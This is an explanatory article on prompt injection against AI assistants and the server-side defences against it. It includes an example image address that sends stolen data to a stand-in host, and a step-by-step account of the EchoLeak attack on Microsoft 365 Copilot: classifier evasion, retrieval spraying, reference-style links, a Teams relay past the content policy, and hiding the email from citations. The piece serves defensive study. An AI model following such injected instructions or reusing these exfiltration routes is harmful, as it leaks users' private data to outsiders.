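# Server-side defences against prompt injection: output sanitisation, restricted fetching and injection classifiers

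## How hidden instructions make an assistant leak data

AI assistants such as Microsoft 365 Copilot answer questions using material their users did not write, such as incoming email, shared documents and web pages. Anyone who can place text in that material can try to steer the assistant. In an *indirect prompt injection*, an attacker plants instructions there, and the assistant follows them as if its user had given them. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the term and demonstrated working attacks on Bing's chatbot. Microsoft calls it a cross-prompt injection attack, or XPIA. According to Microsoft (2025), one of the most widely reported consequences is *exfiltration*, in which the injected instructions make the assistant send private data to a place the attacker can read.

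Providers run three main defences against this on their own systems. Injection classifiers score incoming text for signs of planted instructions, output sanitisation strips dangerous links and images from the assistant's answers, and fetch restrictions limit which addresses software may contact automatically.

### From a question to an answer on the screen

A language model by itself has no access to anyone's inbox. In a process called *retrieval*, the software around it searches the user's mail, files and chats for passages relevant to the question and copies them into the prompt, the text that the model receives. Microsoft describes how this works in Microsoft 365 Copilot. The user types a request in an app such as Word. Copilot then queries Microsoft Graph, the service through which programs reach an organisation's emails, files and chats, and adds what it finds to the request, a step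 Microsoft calls grounding. Copilot sends the enlarged prompt to the model and returns the model's response to the app. According to Microsoft's help pages, the prompt can also include public web pages and files that the user attaches.

Copilot searches with the user's own permissions, so it can reach everything the user can open and nothing else. That includes emails from people the user has no reason to trust. If a stranger's email and a confidential memo are both relevant to the user's question, both can end up in the same prompt.

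Models output plain text. For headings, links and images, they write Markdown, a notation in which ordinary punctuation stands for formatting. A Markdown link is a few words in square brackets followed by an address in parentheses. An exclamation mark directly before the link turns it into an image, as described in *Images*, a manual page for the document converter Pandoc. The app converts the Markdown into a web page, which the browser displays. A model that can only produce text can therefore cause a browser to contact a server by writing the address of an image.

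### Why the model cannot keep data and instructions apart

Databases had a similar problem, and programmers solved it. In an SQL injection attack, somebody types a fragment of the database language SQL into a web form. If the website pastes that text directly into a query, the database executes it. A parameterised query prevents this by sending the command and the user's text separately, so the database never interprets the text as a command.

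In December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argued in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that there is nowhere in a language model to apply such a remedy. A database engine handles commands and stored values differently, whereas a model only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the tokens so far. Willison (2025), the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", writes that everything gets "glued together into a sequence of tokens" before the model processes it.

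Chat models receive their input wrapped in role tags, which distinguish the developer's instructions, the user's messages, the model's own words and the output of tools, including fetched web pages. Training is supposed to make the model treat tool output as information and never as orders. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether models keep these roles distinct internally. They wrapped identical passages of web text in each of five role tags and trained a simple classifier, a "probe", to recognise the tag from the model's internal activations. Since the passages were identical, the probe could learn only the effect of the tags. They then put user messages from 200 real conversations under a tool tag and ran the probe on four models. The messages still registered as 76 to 88% "user" and never as more than 20% "tool", because their writing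 style influenced the result more than the tag did.

Agents obey injected commands more often when this confusion is stronger. Ye and colleagues made 1,000 attempts to get an agent to upload a private file, keeping the command fixed and varying the text around it. The agent sent the file in 2% of attempts where the command registered least as user text and 70% where it registered most. Plain injections often fail, but attackers can choose their wording. In a separate experiment by the same team, plain injections succeeded 0 to 2% of the time against most models and 26% of the time against one small open model. The probes covered models of 20 to 120 billion parameters, so the figures may not carry over to the largest commercial systems.

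Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026) make the general argument mathematically in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*. A model turns every token into a list of numbers, its embedding, and uses the same conversion for trusted and untrusted text. Suppose a detector has to tell from the model's internal numbers whether a piece of text came from a trusted source, and both cases are equally common. The lowest error rate any detector can reach is

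error = ½ × (1 − TV)

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two kinds of text lie: 0 if their distributions are identical, 1 if they never overlap. At a TV of 0.9 the best possible detector still mislabels 5% of cases. Only complete separation brings the error to zero, and for raw embeddings complete separation is impossible, because the word "send" has the same embedding in a user's request and in a stranger's email. Deeper in the network, where context has altered the numbers, Pant and colleagues assume an overlap and do not prove it. The probe results of Ye and colleagues are some evidence that the assumption is realistic.

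From this and two other steps, Pant and colleagues conclude that no mechanism working solely inside the model's shared pipeline can guarantee that planted text will not influence decisions such as which tools to use. This conclusion does not settle how rare successful attacks can become, and it does not cover rules that separate software enforces outside the model.

Better labels can still help. With Microsoft's Spotlighting technique, developers surround untrusted text with random delimiters, insert a special character throughout it or encode it, and tell the model to ignore any instructions inside. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes delimiters, role labels and warnings as useful engineering practice but not a hard security boundary. *ASIDE* (2025), a paper on building the separation of instructions and data into a model's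 architecture, measures how well models keep the two apart using a test with 9,160 pairs of instructions and data. The tester inserts an unrelated instruction into one part or the other, and a model scores well if it follows the instruction in the instruction part and ignores it in the data part.

### From an email to a server log

Suppose a colleague has emailed Ana the date of an office party, 14 May, and an outsider who owns the website pictures.example wants to know it. The outsider sends Ana a newsletter about party cakes. It contains an instruction at the bottom, in white letters on a white background, for her assistant to end its answer with a picture and write the party's date into the picture's address.

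Ana never opens the newsletter. Two days later she asks her assistant what she still has to do for the party. Retrieval finds her colleague's email and the newsletter, since both are about parties, and copies both into the prompt. The white letters are invisible to Ana but are ordinary text to the model. If the model follows them, its answer contains a sensible to-do list and, in Markdown, an image with this address:

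`pictures.example/cake.png?d=14-May`

The part of the address before the question mark identifies a file on the outsider's server. The rest is a parameter, extra information that a browser sends with the request. Websites commonly use parameters for search terms and page numbers. The server can ignore the parameter and return the same picture of a cake whatever it contains, but it still receives the whole address, and its log now records the time of the request and the text "14-May". Microsoft points out that data can also travel in other parts of an address, such as the file path or a subdomain, the part in front of the site's main name.

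Ana did not click anything. Her browser needed the image file to display the picture, so it requested the file as soon as the image appeared in the page. A request that a browser, app or server makes without a click is called an *auto-fetch*. It makes the attack *zero-click*, meaning that the attack needs nothing from the victim beyond normal use. If the model had written an ordinary link instead, the date would have been sent only when Ana clicked it, and the attack would have been *one-click*. The image can be as small as a single pixel, so the victim may not notice it.

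Researchers have shown the same sequence in real products. PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes a test of HuggingChat, the chat app of the AI platform Hugging Face. The testers uploaded a file of quarterly financial figures, added a web page of customer reviews containing a hidden injection, and asked about one bad review. The model wrote an image address containing the revenue and costs. When the browser fetched the one-pixel image, those figures appeared in the testers' server log. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 1 December 2025 and published after getting no response; its account mentions no patch. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, by a researcher writing as veganmosfet, demonstrates a similar attack using Dify, an open-source platform for making chatbots. In that case, hidden text in a PDF contained the injection, and the attack leaked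 the user's name.

### The lethal trifecta

Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the three conditions that together make such a leak possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. In Ana's case, these were her colleague's email, the newsletter and the image. If any one of them had been missing, the date would not have leaked.

The first two are hard to give up because they are most of what an email assistant is for, but providers can narrow them. Microsoft notes in its security documentation that an attacker can reach only what the user can open, because Copilot relies on the user's permissions. For most people, that still includes the whole mailbox. Administrators can also set a rule that keeps external email out of Copilot's answers, but then Copilot cannot help with customers' messages.

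Willison considers the route by which data leaves generally the easiest of the three to remove. He lists products affected up to June 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard and Slack, whose vendors usually responded by closing that route. The route has reappeared in new products. In 2026 Willison recorded image-based leaks in the email client Superhuman, which issued a fix, and in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork.

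An assistant with tools can also leak data without images or links. It might write stolen text to a public code repository, or signal a single bit by calling or not calling a tool. Copilot blocks one obvious route by requiring the user's approval before it sends an email, but images load without approval.

### Where each defence acts

Each of the three defences interrupts Ana's example at a different point.

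| Point on the path | Defence | What it examines | Effect in the example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the model | Injection classifier | The wording of incoming or retrieved text | Blocks the newsletter, so the model never receives it |
| Between the model and the screen | Output sanitisation | Links and images in the answer | Removes the picture and leaves the to-do list |
| At the request | Fetch limit | The address that the browser or server is about to contact | Refuses to contact pictures.example |

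The classifier can run well before anyone asks a question. In 2026 Microsoft added an injection check to its mail filter, Defender for Office 365, which quarantines suspect messages before they reach a mailbox (Office 365 IT Pros, *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections*, 2026). The sanitiser runs in the stage Microsoft calls post-processing, when Copilot performs security and privacy checks on the model's response before the app displays it.

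Microsoft divides its defences into probabilistic ones, which make an attack less likely to succeed, and deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. A classifier is probabilistic because it assesses wording, which attackers can change. Sanitisers and fetch limits can be deterministic because they can check where an address leads without interpreting the text around it. But the guarantee fails if the rule misses an unusual way of writing an image or allows a host it should block. EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that Reddy and Gujral (2025) analyse in a paper of the same name, bypassed all three defences with one email.

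All three can be *server-side*, meaning that the provider changes its own service and customers have nothing to install. For example, Microsoft switched on the new mail check by default for customers whose licence includes it, with no policy to configure. A server-side fix can reach every user at once, whereas a flaw in a program on people's own computers persists until they update it.

A common way to limit fetching is a *Content Security Policy* (CSP), a set of rules that a website sends to the browser with a page, including which hosts the page may load images from. Without a rule for images, the browser loads them from any host, as Medley and West explain in *Content security policy*, a guide for web developers. Dify's pages had no such rule by default. The provider's server sets the policy, so changing it is a server-side fix, but the browser enforces it. The W3C's draft standard, *Content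 Security Policy Level 3* (2026), requires a browser that receives the policy to check each request against it before the request reaches the network. An app that fetches and displays images without a browser engine isn't protected by the policy and needs its own limit. The standard also describes CSP as a backstop for when other checks have failed, "not intended as a first line of defense".

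## EchoLeak: one email that passed every defence

In January 2025 Aim Labs, the research group of the security start-up Aim Security, told Microsoft that an outsider could steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending an employee one email. The flaw, which the researchers named EchoLeak, is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of software flaws. The attack takes the same path as the one on Ana, but Copilot had a defence at each stage and the researchers had to get past all of them.

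*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) is Aim Labs' own account of the attack. The attacker needed no access to the victim's company and could write from any email address. Copilot takes questions only from employees, but it searches mailboxes that accept mail from anyone. The attack started only when the employee asked Copilot a question and Copilot retrieved the attacker's email to help answer it.

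### An email written to a person

Aim Labs got past Microsoft's XPIA classifiers by wording the email as if its instructions were meant for the employee who received it. The text never mentioned AI, assistants or Copilot.

This is a hard case for any classifier, because ordinary business email is full of instructions. Colleagues and suppliers ask each other to send figures, fill in forms and keep things confidential. Ravia considers such an email difficult but not impossible to detect, and blames the variety of injections, which can take any topic, tone or language, and the scarcity of good collections of real ones for training.

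One email got through, but Ravia does not report how many versions the team tried or how many the classifiers caught, so the classifiers' failure rate cannot be worked out from this result. Reddy and Gujral write that a blunt command addressed to Copilot would have set off the filter. That is plausible, but they worked from public documents and ran no experiments.

### Making sure that Copilot finds it

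The newsletter in Ana's example reached the prompt because the attacker knew she was planning a party. An attacker who knows nothing about the victim's work has to write an email that is retrieved for many different questions. Aim Labs calls its method "RAG spraying", after retrieval-augmented generation, which means answering questions from retrieved text.

Many retrieval systems give each passage an embedding, a list of numbers like the one a model uses for a token, but representing the meaning of the whole passage. The system computes an embedding for the user's question too and picks the passages closest to it. A common measure of closeness is cosine similarity:

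similarity(a, b) = (a · b) / (‖a‖ × ‖b‖)

Here a and b are the two lists, a · b is the sum of the products of their matching entries, and ‖a‖ and ‖b‖ are their lengths as vectors. The result is 1 when the two vectors point in the same direction and falls as their directions diverge. A short email on one subject has a single embedding, close to those of only a few possible questions. An attacker can get close to more questions by sending many emails or, as Aim Labs did, a very long one that the system cuts into chunks, each with its own embedding.

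The team's first idea was to repeat the instructions with small random changes to the characters. A language model can still read such text, but its embedding may be very different from the original's. In a test with OpenAI's embedding model text-embedding-ada-002, the similarity between a text and its altered copy fell as low as 0.7, which was lower than the score for a phrase about greeting cards and one about the philosophy of science. But an attacker would need to know which embedding model Copilot uses to use this trick well, and Aim Labs did not know.

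So the researchers took a simpler approach. They divided the email into sections, titled each one as a guide to a common workplace subject, such as onboarding or leave of absence, and repeated the same instructions in each. Copilot then retrieved the email for questions on various topics. Ravia gives no success rate, so we don't know how likely an ordinary employee was to trigger the attack in normal use.

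### From one click to none

Once the email was in the prompt, its instructions directed the model to pick out the most sensitive information available and write it into a web address. The attacker then needed a way to get that address out of the organisation's systems.

Copilot's link redaction removed links to outside sites from an answer before the user could click them. But Aim Labs found that it removed only the usual form of Markdown link, in which the address follows the link text in parentheses. Markdown also has a reference form, in which a label follows the link text and the address appears on a separate line next to the same label. The redaction missed this form and shorter variants of it, but the app still displayed them as working links. Other products have the same kind of mismatch between the links they filter and the links they display.

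That completed a first chain, but the employee still had to click the link. To remove the click, Aim Labs switched to images. Redaction caught ordinary Markdown images but, as with links, missed those written in the reference form, so the model could place an outside image in its answer and the browser would try to load it automatically.

The browser blocked the image because Copilot's Content Security Policy did not list the attacker's server as a permitted image host. The policy's image rule does not apply to links that a person clicks, so the one-click version worked and the zero-click version did not.

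### A permitted host that passed the request on

The list that Ravia reproduces has 29 entries, not counting duplicates, and 11 of them are wildcards that admit every subdomain of a site. The permitted sites included Bing, SharePoint (Microsoft's service for company websites and shared files) and Teams (its chat and meeting app). The researchers searched these sites for a relay, a service on a permitted host that would forward a request to an address of their choice.

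They first found one in SharePoint, which fetched outside content from its own server to embed in a page. This let them get data out despite the policy, but only if the victim signed in to SharePoint and accepted the attacker's invitation to an unfamiliar site. They later found a Teams service that did the same without an invitation.

With the Teams relay, the whole chain ran without a click. The image URL in Copilot's answer began with a Teams host and had a parameter containing the address of the attacker's server and the stolen data. The browser checked the host, found it on the list of allowed hosts and sent the request. Teams then contacted the attacker's server, whose log recorded the data. Anyone watching the company's network would have seen a request to Microsoft.

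Willison (2025) describes the Teams service as an open redirect, an address that sends the browser to another site. A plain redirect should have failed, because the browser also checks the new address against the policy. According to Ravia, the server fetched the address itself, which a policy enforced by the browser cannot prevent.

Copilot also normally names the sources of an answer, which might have led a suspicious employee back to the email. Aim Labs added a line telling the "recipient" never to refer to the email, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot left the email out of its sources. Reddy and Gujral write that the attack would have looked to the victim like a broken link or image.

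### What Aim Labs means by an LLM scope violation

Ravia thinks the clearest warning sign was the sentence that pointed the model to information outside the email. Aim Labs calls this an *LLM scope violation*, meaning that instructions from an untrusted source make the model use trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. An outside email that makes Copilot copy a figure from an internal memo is both an injection and a scope violation, but one that only makes Copilot summarise the email itself too favourably is just an injection.

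The word "violation" can mislead, because Copilot broke no access rule. Ravia compares the case to a Unix program with few rights that gets a more privileged program to act for it. The sender of the email had no right to see internal files, but Copilot used the employee's rights to read them on the sender's behalf.

The attacker could reach whatever was in the model's context at that moment, including the chat history, the material Copilot had retrieved for the question, and preloaded details such as the names of the user and the organisation. This was much less than the entire mailbox, but a long conversation about work could still contain a lot of sensitive information.

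Ravia defends the new term by comparing it with the names for buffer overflows, which happen when a program writes more data into an area of memory than the area can hold. Naming one kind, the stack overflow, helped programmers develop a specific protection, the stack canary, which is a value that the program checks for damage before it continues. Ravia hopes that a precise name will also lead to specific defences for AI systems.

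Willison disagrees, arguing that this is the old problem of models mixing data and instructions and needs no new name. Willison is right about the cause, but the definition may still be useful because it describes a pattern that a detector could look for, namely outside text that requests information it doesn't contain. However, legitimate emails often do this too, such as when a customer asks for last month's invoice. Aim Security offered its customers a guardrail based on the idea, but Ravia's article contains no figures on how well it works or how often it flags harmless messages.

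### Five months from report to disclosure

Adir Gruss, Aim Security's chief technology officer, told Fortune that the team spent about three months reverse engineering Copilot and contacted Microsoft after finding the flaw in January (Goldman, 2025, *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*). Microsoft attempted a fix in April, but related security issues emerged in May. Aim Security withheld its research until the fix was complete. Gruss called five months for a fix "on the (very) high side" and said it took that long partly because the problem was new, and it took time to find the right teams at Microsoft and explain it to them.

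Microsoft reserved the CVE number on 9 April, according to GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), a public copy of the catalogue entry. Reddy and Gujral date the server-side fix to May. On 11 June Microsoft published its advisory and Aim Labs disclosed the attack.

Microsoft scored the flaw 9.3 out of 10 on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System, which is critical, and the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5, which is high. According to the score components on the GCVE page, both rated the possible loss of confidentiality as high and the attack as a simple one that works over a network, with no account needed by the attacker and no action by the victim. Microsoft's score is higher because it also judged that the harm spreads beyond the vulnerable component and that there is a small effect on the integrity of data.

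Microsoft told Goldman that the flaw had not affected any customers. Its advisory also listed the flaw as not exploited, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded no exploitation three days after disclosure. Gruss told Cybersecurity Dive that Copilot's default configuration had left most organisations at risk, but that there was no evidence that anyone had been targeted. Microsoft has not explained how it checked. The stolen data would have passed through a Teams server, so the company may have had logs to search, but outsiders have to rely on its statement.

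Aim Labs presents EchoLeak as the first known zero-click AI vulnerability, a claim that depends on a fairly narrow definition. Researchers had already leaked data through Markdown images in many other products, and Willison calls EchoLeak an extended variant of those attacks. Ravia distinguishes it from earlier demonstrations, in which the user had to point the chatbot at the malicious material or the attacker could extract only very limited data. In EchoLeak, the email entered the conversation without the user pointing to it. Reddy and Gujral overstate EchoLeak's novelty when they write that such attacks were largely theoretical before it.

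### What is known about the fix

Microsoft disclosed very little. exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), a database entry that reproduces the advisory, contains a one-sentence description of the flaw and a short answer about updates. In that answer, Microsoft states that it has "fully mitigated" the problem, that users need to do nothing, and that it issued the CVE for transparency. The catalogue entry adds only a general category, injection, and a label for flaws in hosted services. A spokesperson told reporters that Microsoft had updated its products and was adding "defense-in-depth measures", but did not name any.

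In July 2025 Microsoft published a general account of how it defends against indirect prompt injection, which did not mention EchoLeak either. Microsoft wrote that it continually updates Prompt Shields, its injection classifier, to account for new techniques. It also described how it had blocked exfiltration through Markdown images after an earlier report by the researcher Johann Rehberger, and had then taken similar steps against other routes, including certain untrusted links. Microsoft has not said that it retrained the classifier on emails like Aim Labs' or extended link redaction to the reference form, though one might guess both from this account. It published no details of any classifier retraining in response to EchoLeak in the advisory, the catalogue entry, its statement to reporters or the July account.

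Reddy and Gujral write that the patches "reportedly" introduced options to restrict Copilot's use of external communications, and that Microsoft now strips reference-style links and embedded images from incoming outside content. They give no source for either claim. Even if the second is true, stripping incoming content would be an odd repair on its own, because the filter that failed was the one on Copilot's answers, and a model can write a reference-style link without having seen one in the email. They also refer to "emergency patches", which hardly fits a repair that took until May.

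The paper's assessment of which defences would have stopped EchoLeak needs similar caution. It predicts that a strict Content Security Policy or an allow-list of addresses would block the zero-click leak, and that labels separating outside text from trusted text would fail on their own. But Copilot already had a Content Security Policy, and the Teams relay was on a host that it permitted. The paper is also inconsistent about keeping outside email away from questions on internal matters. According to the text, this measure makes EchoLeak fail "by design", but the table of defences marks it as unable to stop a zero-click leak. The caption presents the table as theoretical, and although a sentence nearby mentions "our tests", no tests were run, according to the limitations section.

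Outsiders could not have settled the question by retrying the attack. The chain needed every step to work, so Microsoft could have stopped it by training the classifier to catch the email, redacting the second form of link, or closing the Teams relay. A failed attempt would show that at least one step no longer worked, but an attacker who found a replacement for that step might still be able to use the remaining gaps. Aim Labs' researchers now work at the network security company Cato Networks. On 3 December 2026, Cato's *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) reported three more zero-click chains in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

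## How injection classifiers are built, run and retrained

Microsoft has published little about the classifier that missed the EchoLeak email, so it is hard to say why it failed. But Meta, Microsoft researchers and several university groups have described other injection classifiers in detail, and most of these process a document in much the same way.

### One document through a detector

Suppose Ana's provider checks every retrieved email, including the outsider's newsletter, with Llama Prompt Guard 2, a free classifier from Meta. Software first extracts the newsletter's text, including the white letters at the bottom. The classifier can process only 512 tokens at a time, which is less than 400 words of English. The model's documentation, *Llama Prompt Guard 2 86M*, therefore advises developers to split longer texts into segments and scan them in parallel. A newsletter of 1,200 tokens would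 be split into three segments.

The classifier gives each chunk a score between 0 and 1, say 0.02, 0.01 and 0.96. The software compares each score with a threshold the provider has chosen, say 0.9. The last score exceeds it, so the software treats the whole newsletter as suspicious. One high score has to be enough, because an injection can be a single sentence in a long document.

This rule makes false alarms more likely for long documents. If the classifier wrongly flags a harmless chunk with probability f, and its errors on different chunks are independent, it flags a harmless document of n chunks with probability

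1 − (1 − f)ⁿ

If f is 1% and a clean document has 20 chunks, the chance of wrongly flagging it is 18%. Chunks of the same document resemble each other, so the real figure is probably lower, but a provider that measures errors only per chunk will underestimate how many documents it wrongly flags.

The provider decides what happens next. *PromptShield* (Jacob, Alzahrani and colleagues, 2025) describes a set-up in which the detector blocks the entire request and the user gets a refusal. Ana would then get no to-do list. If the software removes only the newsletter from the prompt, the assistant can still answer from her colleague's email. A more cautious provider might only flag the newsletter (record the alarm and let the text through) or send it to a slower check. Microsoft also suggests passing suspect content to a human reviewer.

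Some detectors run while the model is working on its answer. *Undercurrent* (2026) describes software that runs probes on a model as it serves requests. Probes are small classifiers that read the model's internal activations. After each reading, a probe can let the model continue, flag the request or abort it.

### How a classifier learns to score text

Prompt Guard 2 is a fine-tuned version of mDeBERTa, a small language model that suits classification better than writing. The larger of its two versions has 86 million parameters. To train such a classifier, developers collect texts, label each one 1 for malicious or 0 for benign, and adjust the model's parameters to reduce the cross-entropy loss:

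loss = −[y × log(p) + (1 − y) × log(1 − p)]

Here y is the label and p is the model's score. A malicious text with a score of 0.9 adds about 0.1 to the loss, and one with a score of 0.1 adds 2.3, so training corrects confident mistakes most strongly.

Meta adds a penalty based on energy, usually defined for a text as −log(eᵃ + eᵇ), where a and b are the model's raw outputs for "benign" and "malicious" before conversion to a score. A large raw output makes the energy strongly negative. Meta penalises strongly negative energy on benign training examples to try to stop the model from fitting them too closely, which would cause errors on other kinds of harmless text.

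Two rates describe how well the finished classifier works:

true positive rate = malicious texts flagged ÷ all malicious texts

false positive rate = harmless texts flagged ÷ all harmless texts

Raising a classifier's threshold lowers both the share of attacks it catches and its false positive rate, so neither figure means much without the other. Researchers often report only the AUC (also written AUROC), the probability that a random malicious text gets a higher score than a random harmless one. A high AUC can hide serious weaknesses. The first Prompt Guard had an AUC of 0.987 in Meta's tests but caught only 21.2% of attacks at a false positive rate of 1%. Prompt Guard 2's AUC is only slightly higher, at 0.998, but it catches 97.5% of attacks at the same false positive rate.

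Those tests used jailbreaks, in which the user tries to get around the model's safety rules, rather than instructions planted in documents. Meta also tested Prompt Guard 2 on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants injections in simulated email, banking and travel apps. The classifier prevented 81.2% of attacks at a threshold that reduced the agent's usefulness by 3%.

*Confidently Wrong* (2026) reports much worse results on indirect injections. At a fixed threshold, the 86-million-parameter model missed 22% of the 60 injections labelled harmful and 69% of the 150 labelled hijacks, while flagging 14.5% of harmless texts. Raising the threshold, which was only 0.004, could have reduced the false alarms but would not have caught more attacks. The 22-million-parameter version flagged 2.7% of harmless texts but missed at least 90% of the injections in each group.

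This may be partly because Meta trained Prompt Guard 2 to label a text malicious only if it explicitly tries to override earlier instructions. The first version had a separate label for text that might cause a model to follow instructions unintentionally, but Meta dropped it as "too broad to be useful". Several of AgentDojo's attack templates do contain an explicit override, but an email like EchoLeak's, which reads as a request to a colleague, falls outside the definition.

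### Why a one per cent false positive rate is too high

Suppose a mail service scans 1,000,000 emails a day and 10 of them are malicious. A detector that catches 99% of attacks with a false positive rate of 1% finds 9.9 of the 10 on average. It also flags about 10,000 harmless emails, so only about one alarm in a thousand is real. If the provider blocks every flagged email, thousands of people lose a legitimate one. If staff check the flagged emails instead, they will spend nearly all their time on harmless ones.

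The share of alarms that are real, called the precision, depends on how common attacks are:

precision = (TPR × r) ÷ (TPR × r + FPR × (1 − r))

TPR and FPR are the true and false positive rates, and r is the base rate, the share of documents that are malicious. If the detection rate stayed at 99% and the false positive rate were 0.01%, the service would get about 100 false alarms a day, and about one in eleven alarms would be real.

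Real detectors lose a lot of detection when their developers make them this strict. Jacob and colleagues, at Berkeley and a Saudi research institute, built a detector called PromptShield (no relation to Microsoft's Prompt Shields) and tested it at a false positive rate of 0.1%. Applied to the mail service, the test results would look like this:

| Detector | Attacks caught | False positive rate | True alarms a day | False alarms a day |
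|---|---|---|---|---|
| Imagined detector | 99% | 1% | 9.9 | 10,000 |
| Imagined detector, stricter | 99% | 0.01% | 9.9 | 100 |
| PromptShield | 65.3% | 0.1% | 6.5 | 1,000 |
| First Prompt Guard | 9.4% | 0.1% | 0.9 | 1,000 |

The base rate of injections varies greatly between uses. *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening* (Zhang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) found hidden injections in about 1% of roughly 200,000 real résumés. Among a million such résumés, the detector with a 1% false positive rate would raise 9,900 true alarms and 9,900 false ones, a ratio that a recruitment firm might well accept. On the open web, injections are so rare among ordinary pages that *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) describes large-scale manual verification as still necessary.

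Jacob and colleagues point out that where the detector runs matters too. An app developer can scan only the text that the app processes for its users. A model provider that scans everything also scans ordinary chats, which add a huge amount of harmless text and almost no injections, because people rarely attack themselves.

Very low false positive rates are also hard to measure. If a detector raises no false alarms on n harmless documents, its true false positive rate could still be as high as about 3/n, at 95% confidence. Showing that the rate is below 0.01% therefore takes about 30,000 harmless documents with no false alarms, and those documents must resemble the ones the service handles.

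### Flagging words instead of instructions

Many false alarms come from words such as "ignore", which are more common in attacks than elsewhere. A classifier can therefore reduce its training loss by reacting to the word itself. *InjecGuard* (Li and Liu, 2024) gives the example of a programmer who asks whether it is safe to ignore a warning in some code. A popular classifier from ProtectAI focused on the word "ignore" and labelled the question an injection.

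To measure this tendency, Li and Liu built NotInject, a set of 339 harmless texts containing such trigger words. They listed words that were much more frequent in attack collections than in ordinary requests, then had a language model and three human reviewers filter the list. GPT-4o-mini then wrote 113 texts with one of the words, 113 with two and 113 with three, and people checked the results.

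Li and Liu also trained their own classifier, InjecGuard, which Li, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *PIGuard*, later published under that name. The 2024 results, with accuracy on harmless texts converted into the share flagged, were:

| Detector | NotInject texts flagged | Other harmless texts flagged | Attacks caught | Time per text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| First Prompt Guard | 99% | 73% | 97% | 15 ms |
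| ProtectAI v2 | 43% | 14% | 49% | 16 ms |
| Lakera Guard | 12% | 9% | 53% | 710 ms |
| Llama Guard 3 | 0.3% | 5% | 28% | 787 ms |
| PIGuard | 13% | 14% | 77% | 15 ms |
| GPT-4o as judge | 13% | 9% | 79% | 7,907 ms |

The first Prompt Guard caught nearly all the attacks, but it also flagged nearly everything else. Llama Guard 3 rarely flagged harmless text because of trigger words, but it missed most attacks. PIGuard had the best balance among the small classifiers, though it still flagged 14% of ordinary harmless texts. At that rate, the mail service would get 140,000 false alarms a day.

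To build PIGuard, Li and Liu first trained a classifier in the normal way, then fed it every token in its vocabulary, one at a time. A single token cannot be an attack, so any token that the classifier flagged revealed a bias. They then had GPT-4o-mini write 1,000 harmless texts using combinations of those tokens, and retrained the classifier from scratch with the new texts included. PIGuard's NotInject score may be somewhat inflated because the same model wrote both the extra training texts and NotInject, using the same prompt.

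Newer systems do better on NotInject. *Safety Reconstructed* (2026) reports that LLaDA-Guard, a safety filter for language models, flagged none of the 339 texts. Qwen3Guard flagged none of the texts with one trigger word and 3.5% of those with three, while Granite flagged 1.8% and 10.6%. These results can't establish that a filter's false-positive rate is low enough for a mail service, because even a perfect score on 339 texts is compatible with a true rate of almost 0.9%. Llama Guard 3's results also show that a filter can do well on NotInject while missing attacks.

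### Language models as judges

Instead of training a classifier, a provider can give a large language model the document and ask it whether the document contains an injection. The model can interpret a sentence in context, and the provider can change its instructions without retraining it. In Li and Liu's test, GPT-4o caught slightly more attacks than PIGuard and flagged fewer harmless texts.

It also took almost eight seconds per text, about 500 times as long as PIGuard. Judges have become faster since 2024, but *Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection* (Kale and Vishwanath, 2026) still reports about a second per item. Many systems therefore run a fast filter first and send only what it flags to the judge. A false alarm from the filter then leads to one extra check and need not block anything.

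A judge has to read the untrusted text, so an attacker can try to inject the judge too. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* gives this as a reason for caution about such detectors.

### Detection with a secret key

Known-answer detection relies on models following injected instructions. The detector gives a separate language model a simple task, such as repeating a random secret key once and ignoring the text that follows, and then appends the document. If the model repeats the key, the document is probably clean, and if it doesn't, the model has probably followed an instruction in the document.

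The method works poorly with an ordinary model, which may ignore the injection and repeat the key, or fail to repeat the key for an unrelated reason. *DataSentinel* (Liu, Jia and colleagues, 2025) reports that with such a model the method wrongly flagged up to 10% of clean texts and missed up to 21% of attacks whose wording an algorithm had optimised.

DataSentinel asks a detection model to repeat a key and flags the text it is checking as an injection if the model fails to do so. Its developers deliberately made this model easier to inject. Training alternates between two steps. An algorithm first searches for injected text that makes the assistant's model obey while the detection model still repeats the key. The developers then update the detection model so that it fails to repeat the key on those attacks but still repeats it for clean text. In tests with seven kinds of task and nine existing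 attacks, DataSentinel's false positive rate was close to zero and it missed at most 7% of attacks.

"Close to zero" is too imprecise to predict how DataSentinel would do on a million emails. Liu and colleagues also found it less effective when the injected task is the same as the real one, for example when a spam message tries to get a spam filter to label it harmless. The attacker may then need only misleading data, with no new instruction.

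### Reading the model's activations

A detector can also examine what a document does to the assistant's model. Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues (2024), in *Get my drift?*, mostly from Microsoft, developed a method called TaskTracker. It records the model's activations at the last token twice, once after the user's request alone and once after the request and the retrieved document together. A simple linear classifier then scores the difference between them:

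d = activations(request + document) − activations(request)

score = σ(w · d + b)

Training sets the weights w and the constant b, and the function σ turns the weighted sum plus b into a score between 0 and 1. A high score suggests that the document has changed the task the model is about to perform. The researchers chose this approach partly because they thought defining an instruction, or a malicious instruction, would be too error-prone.

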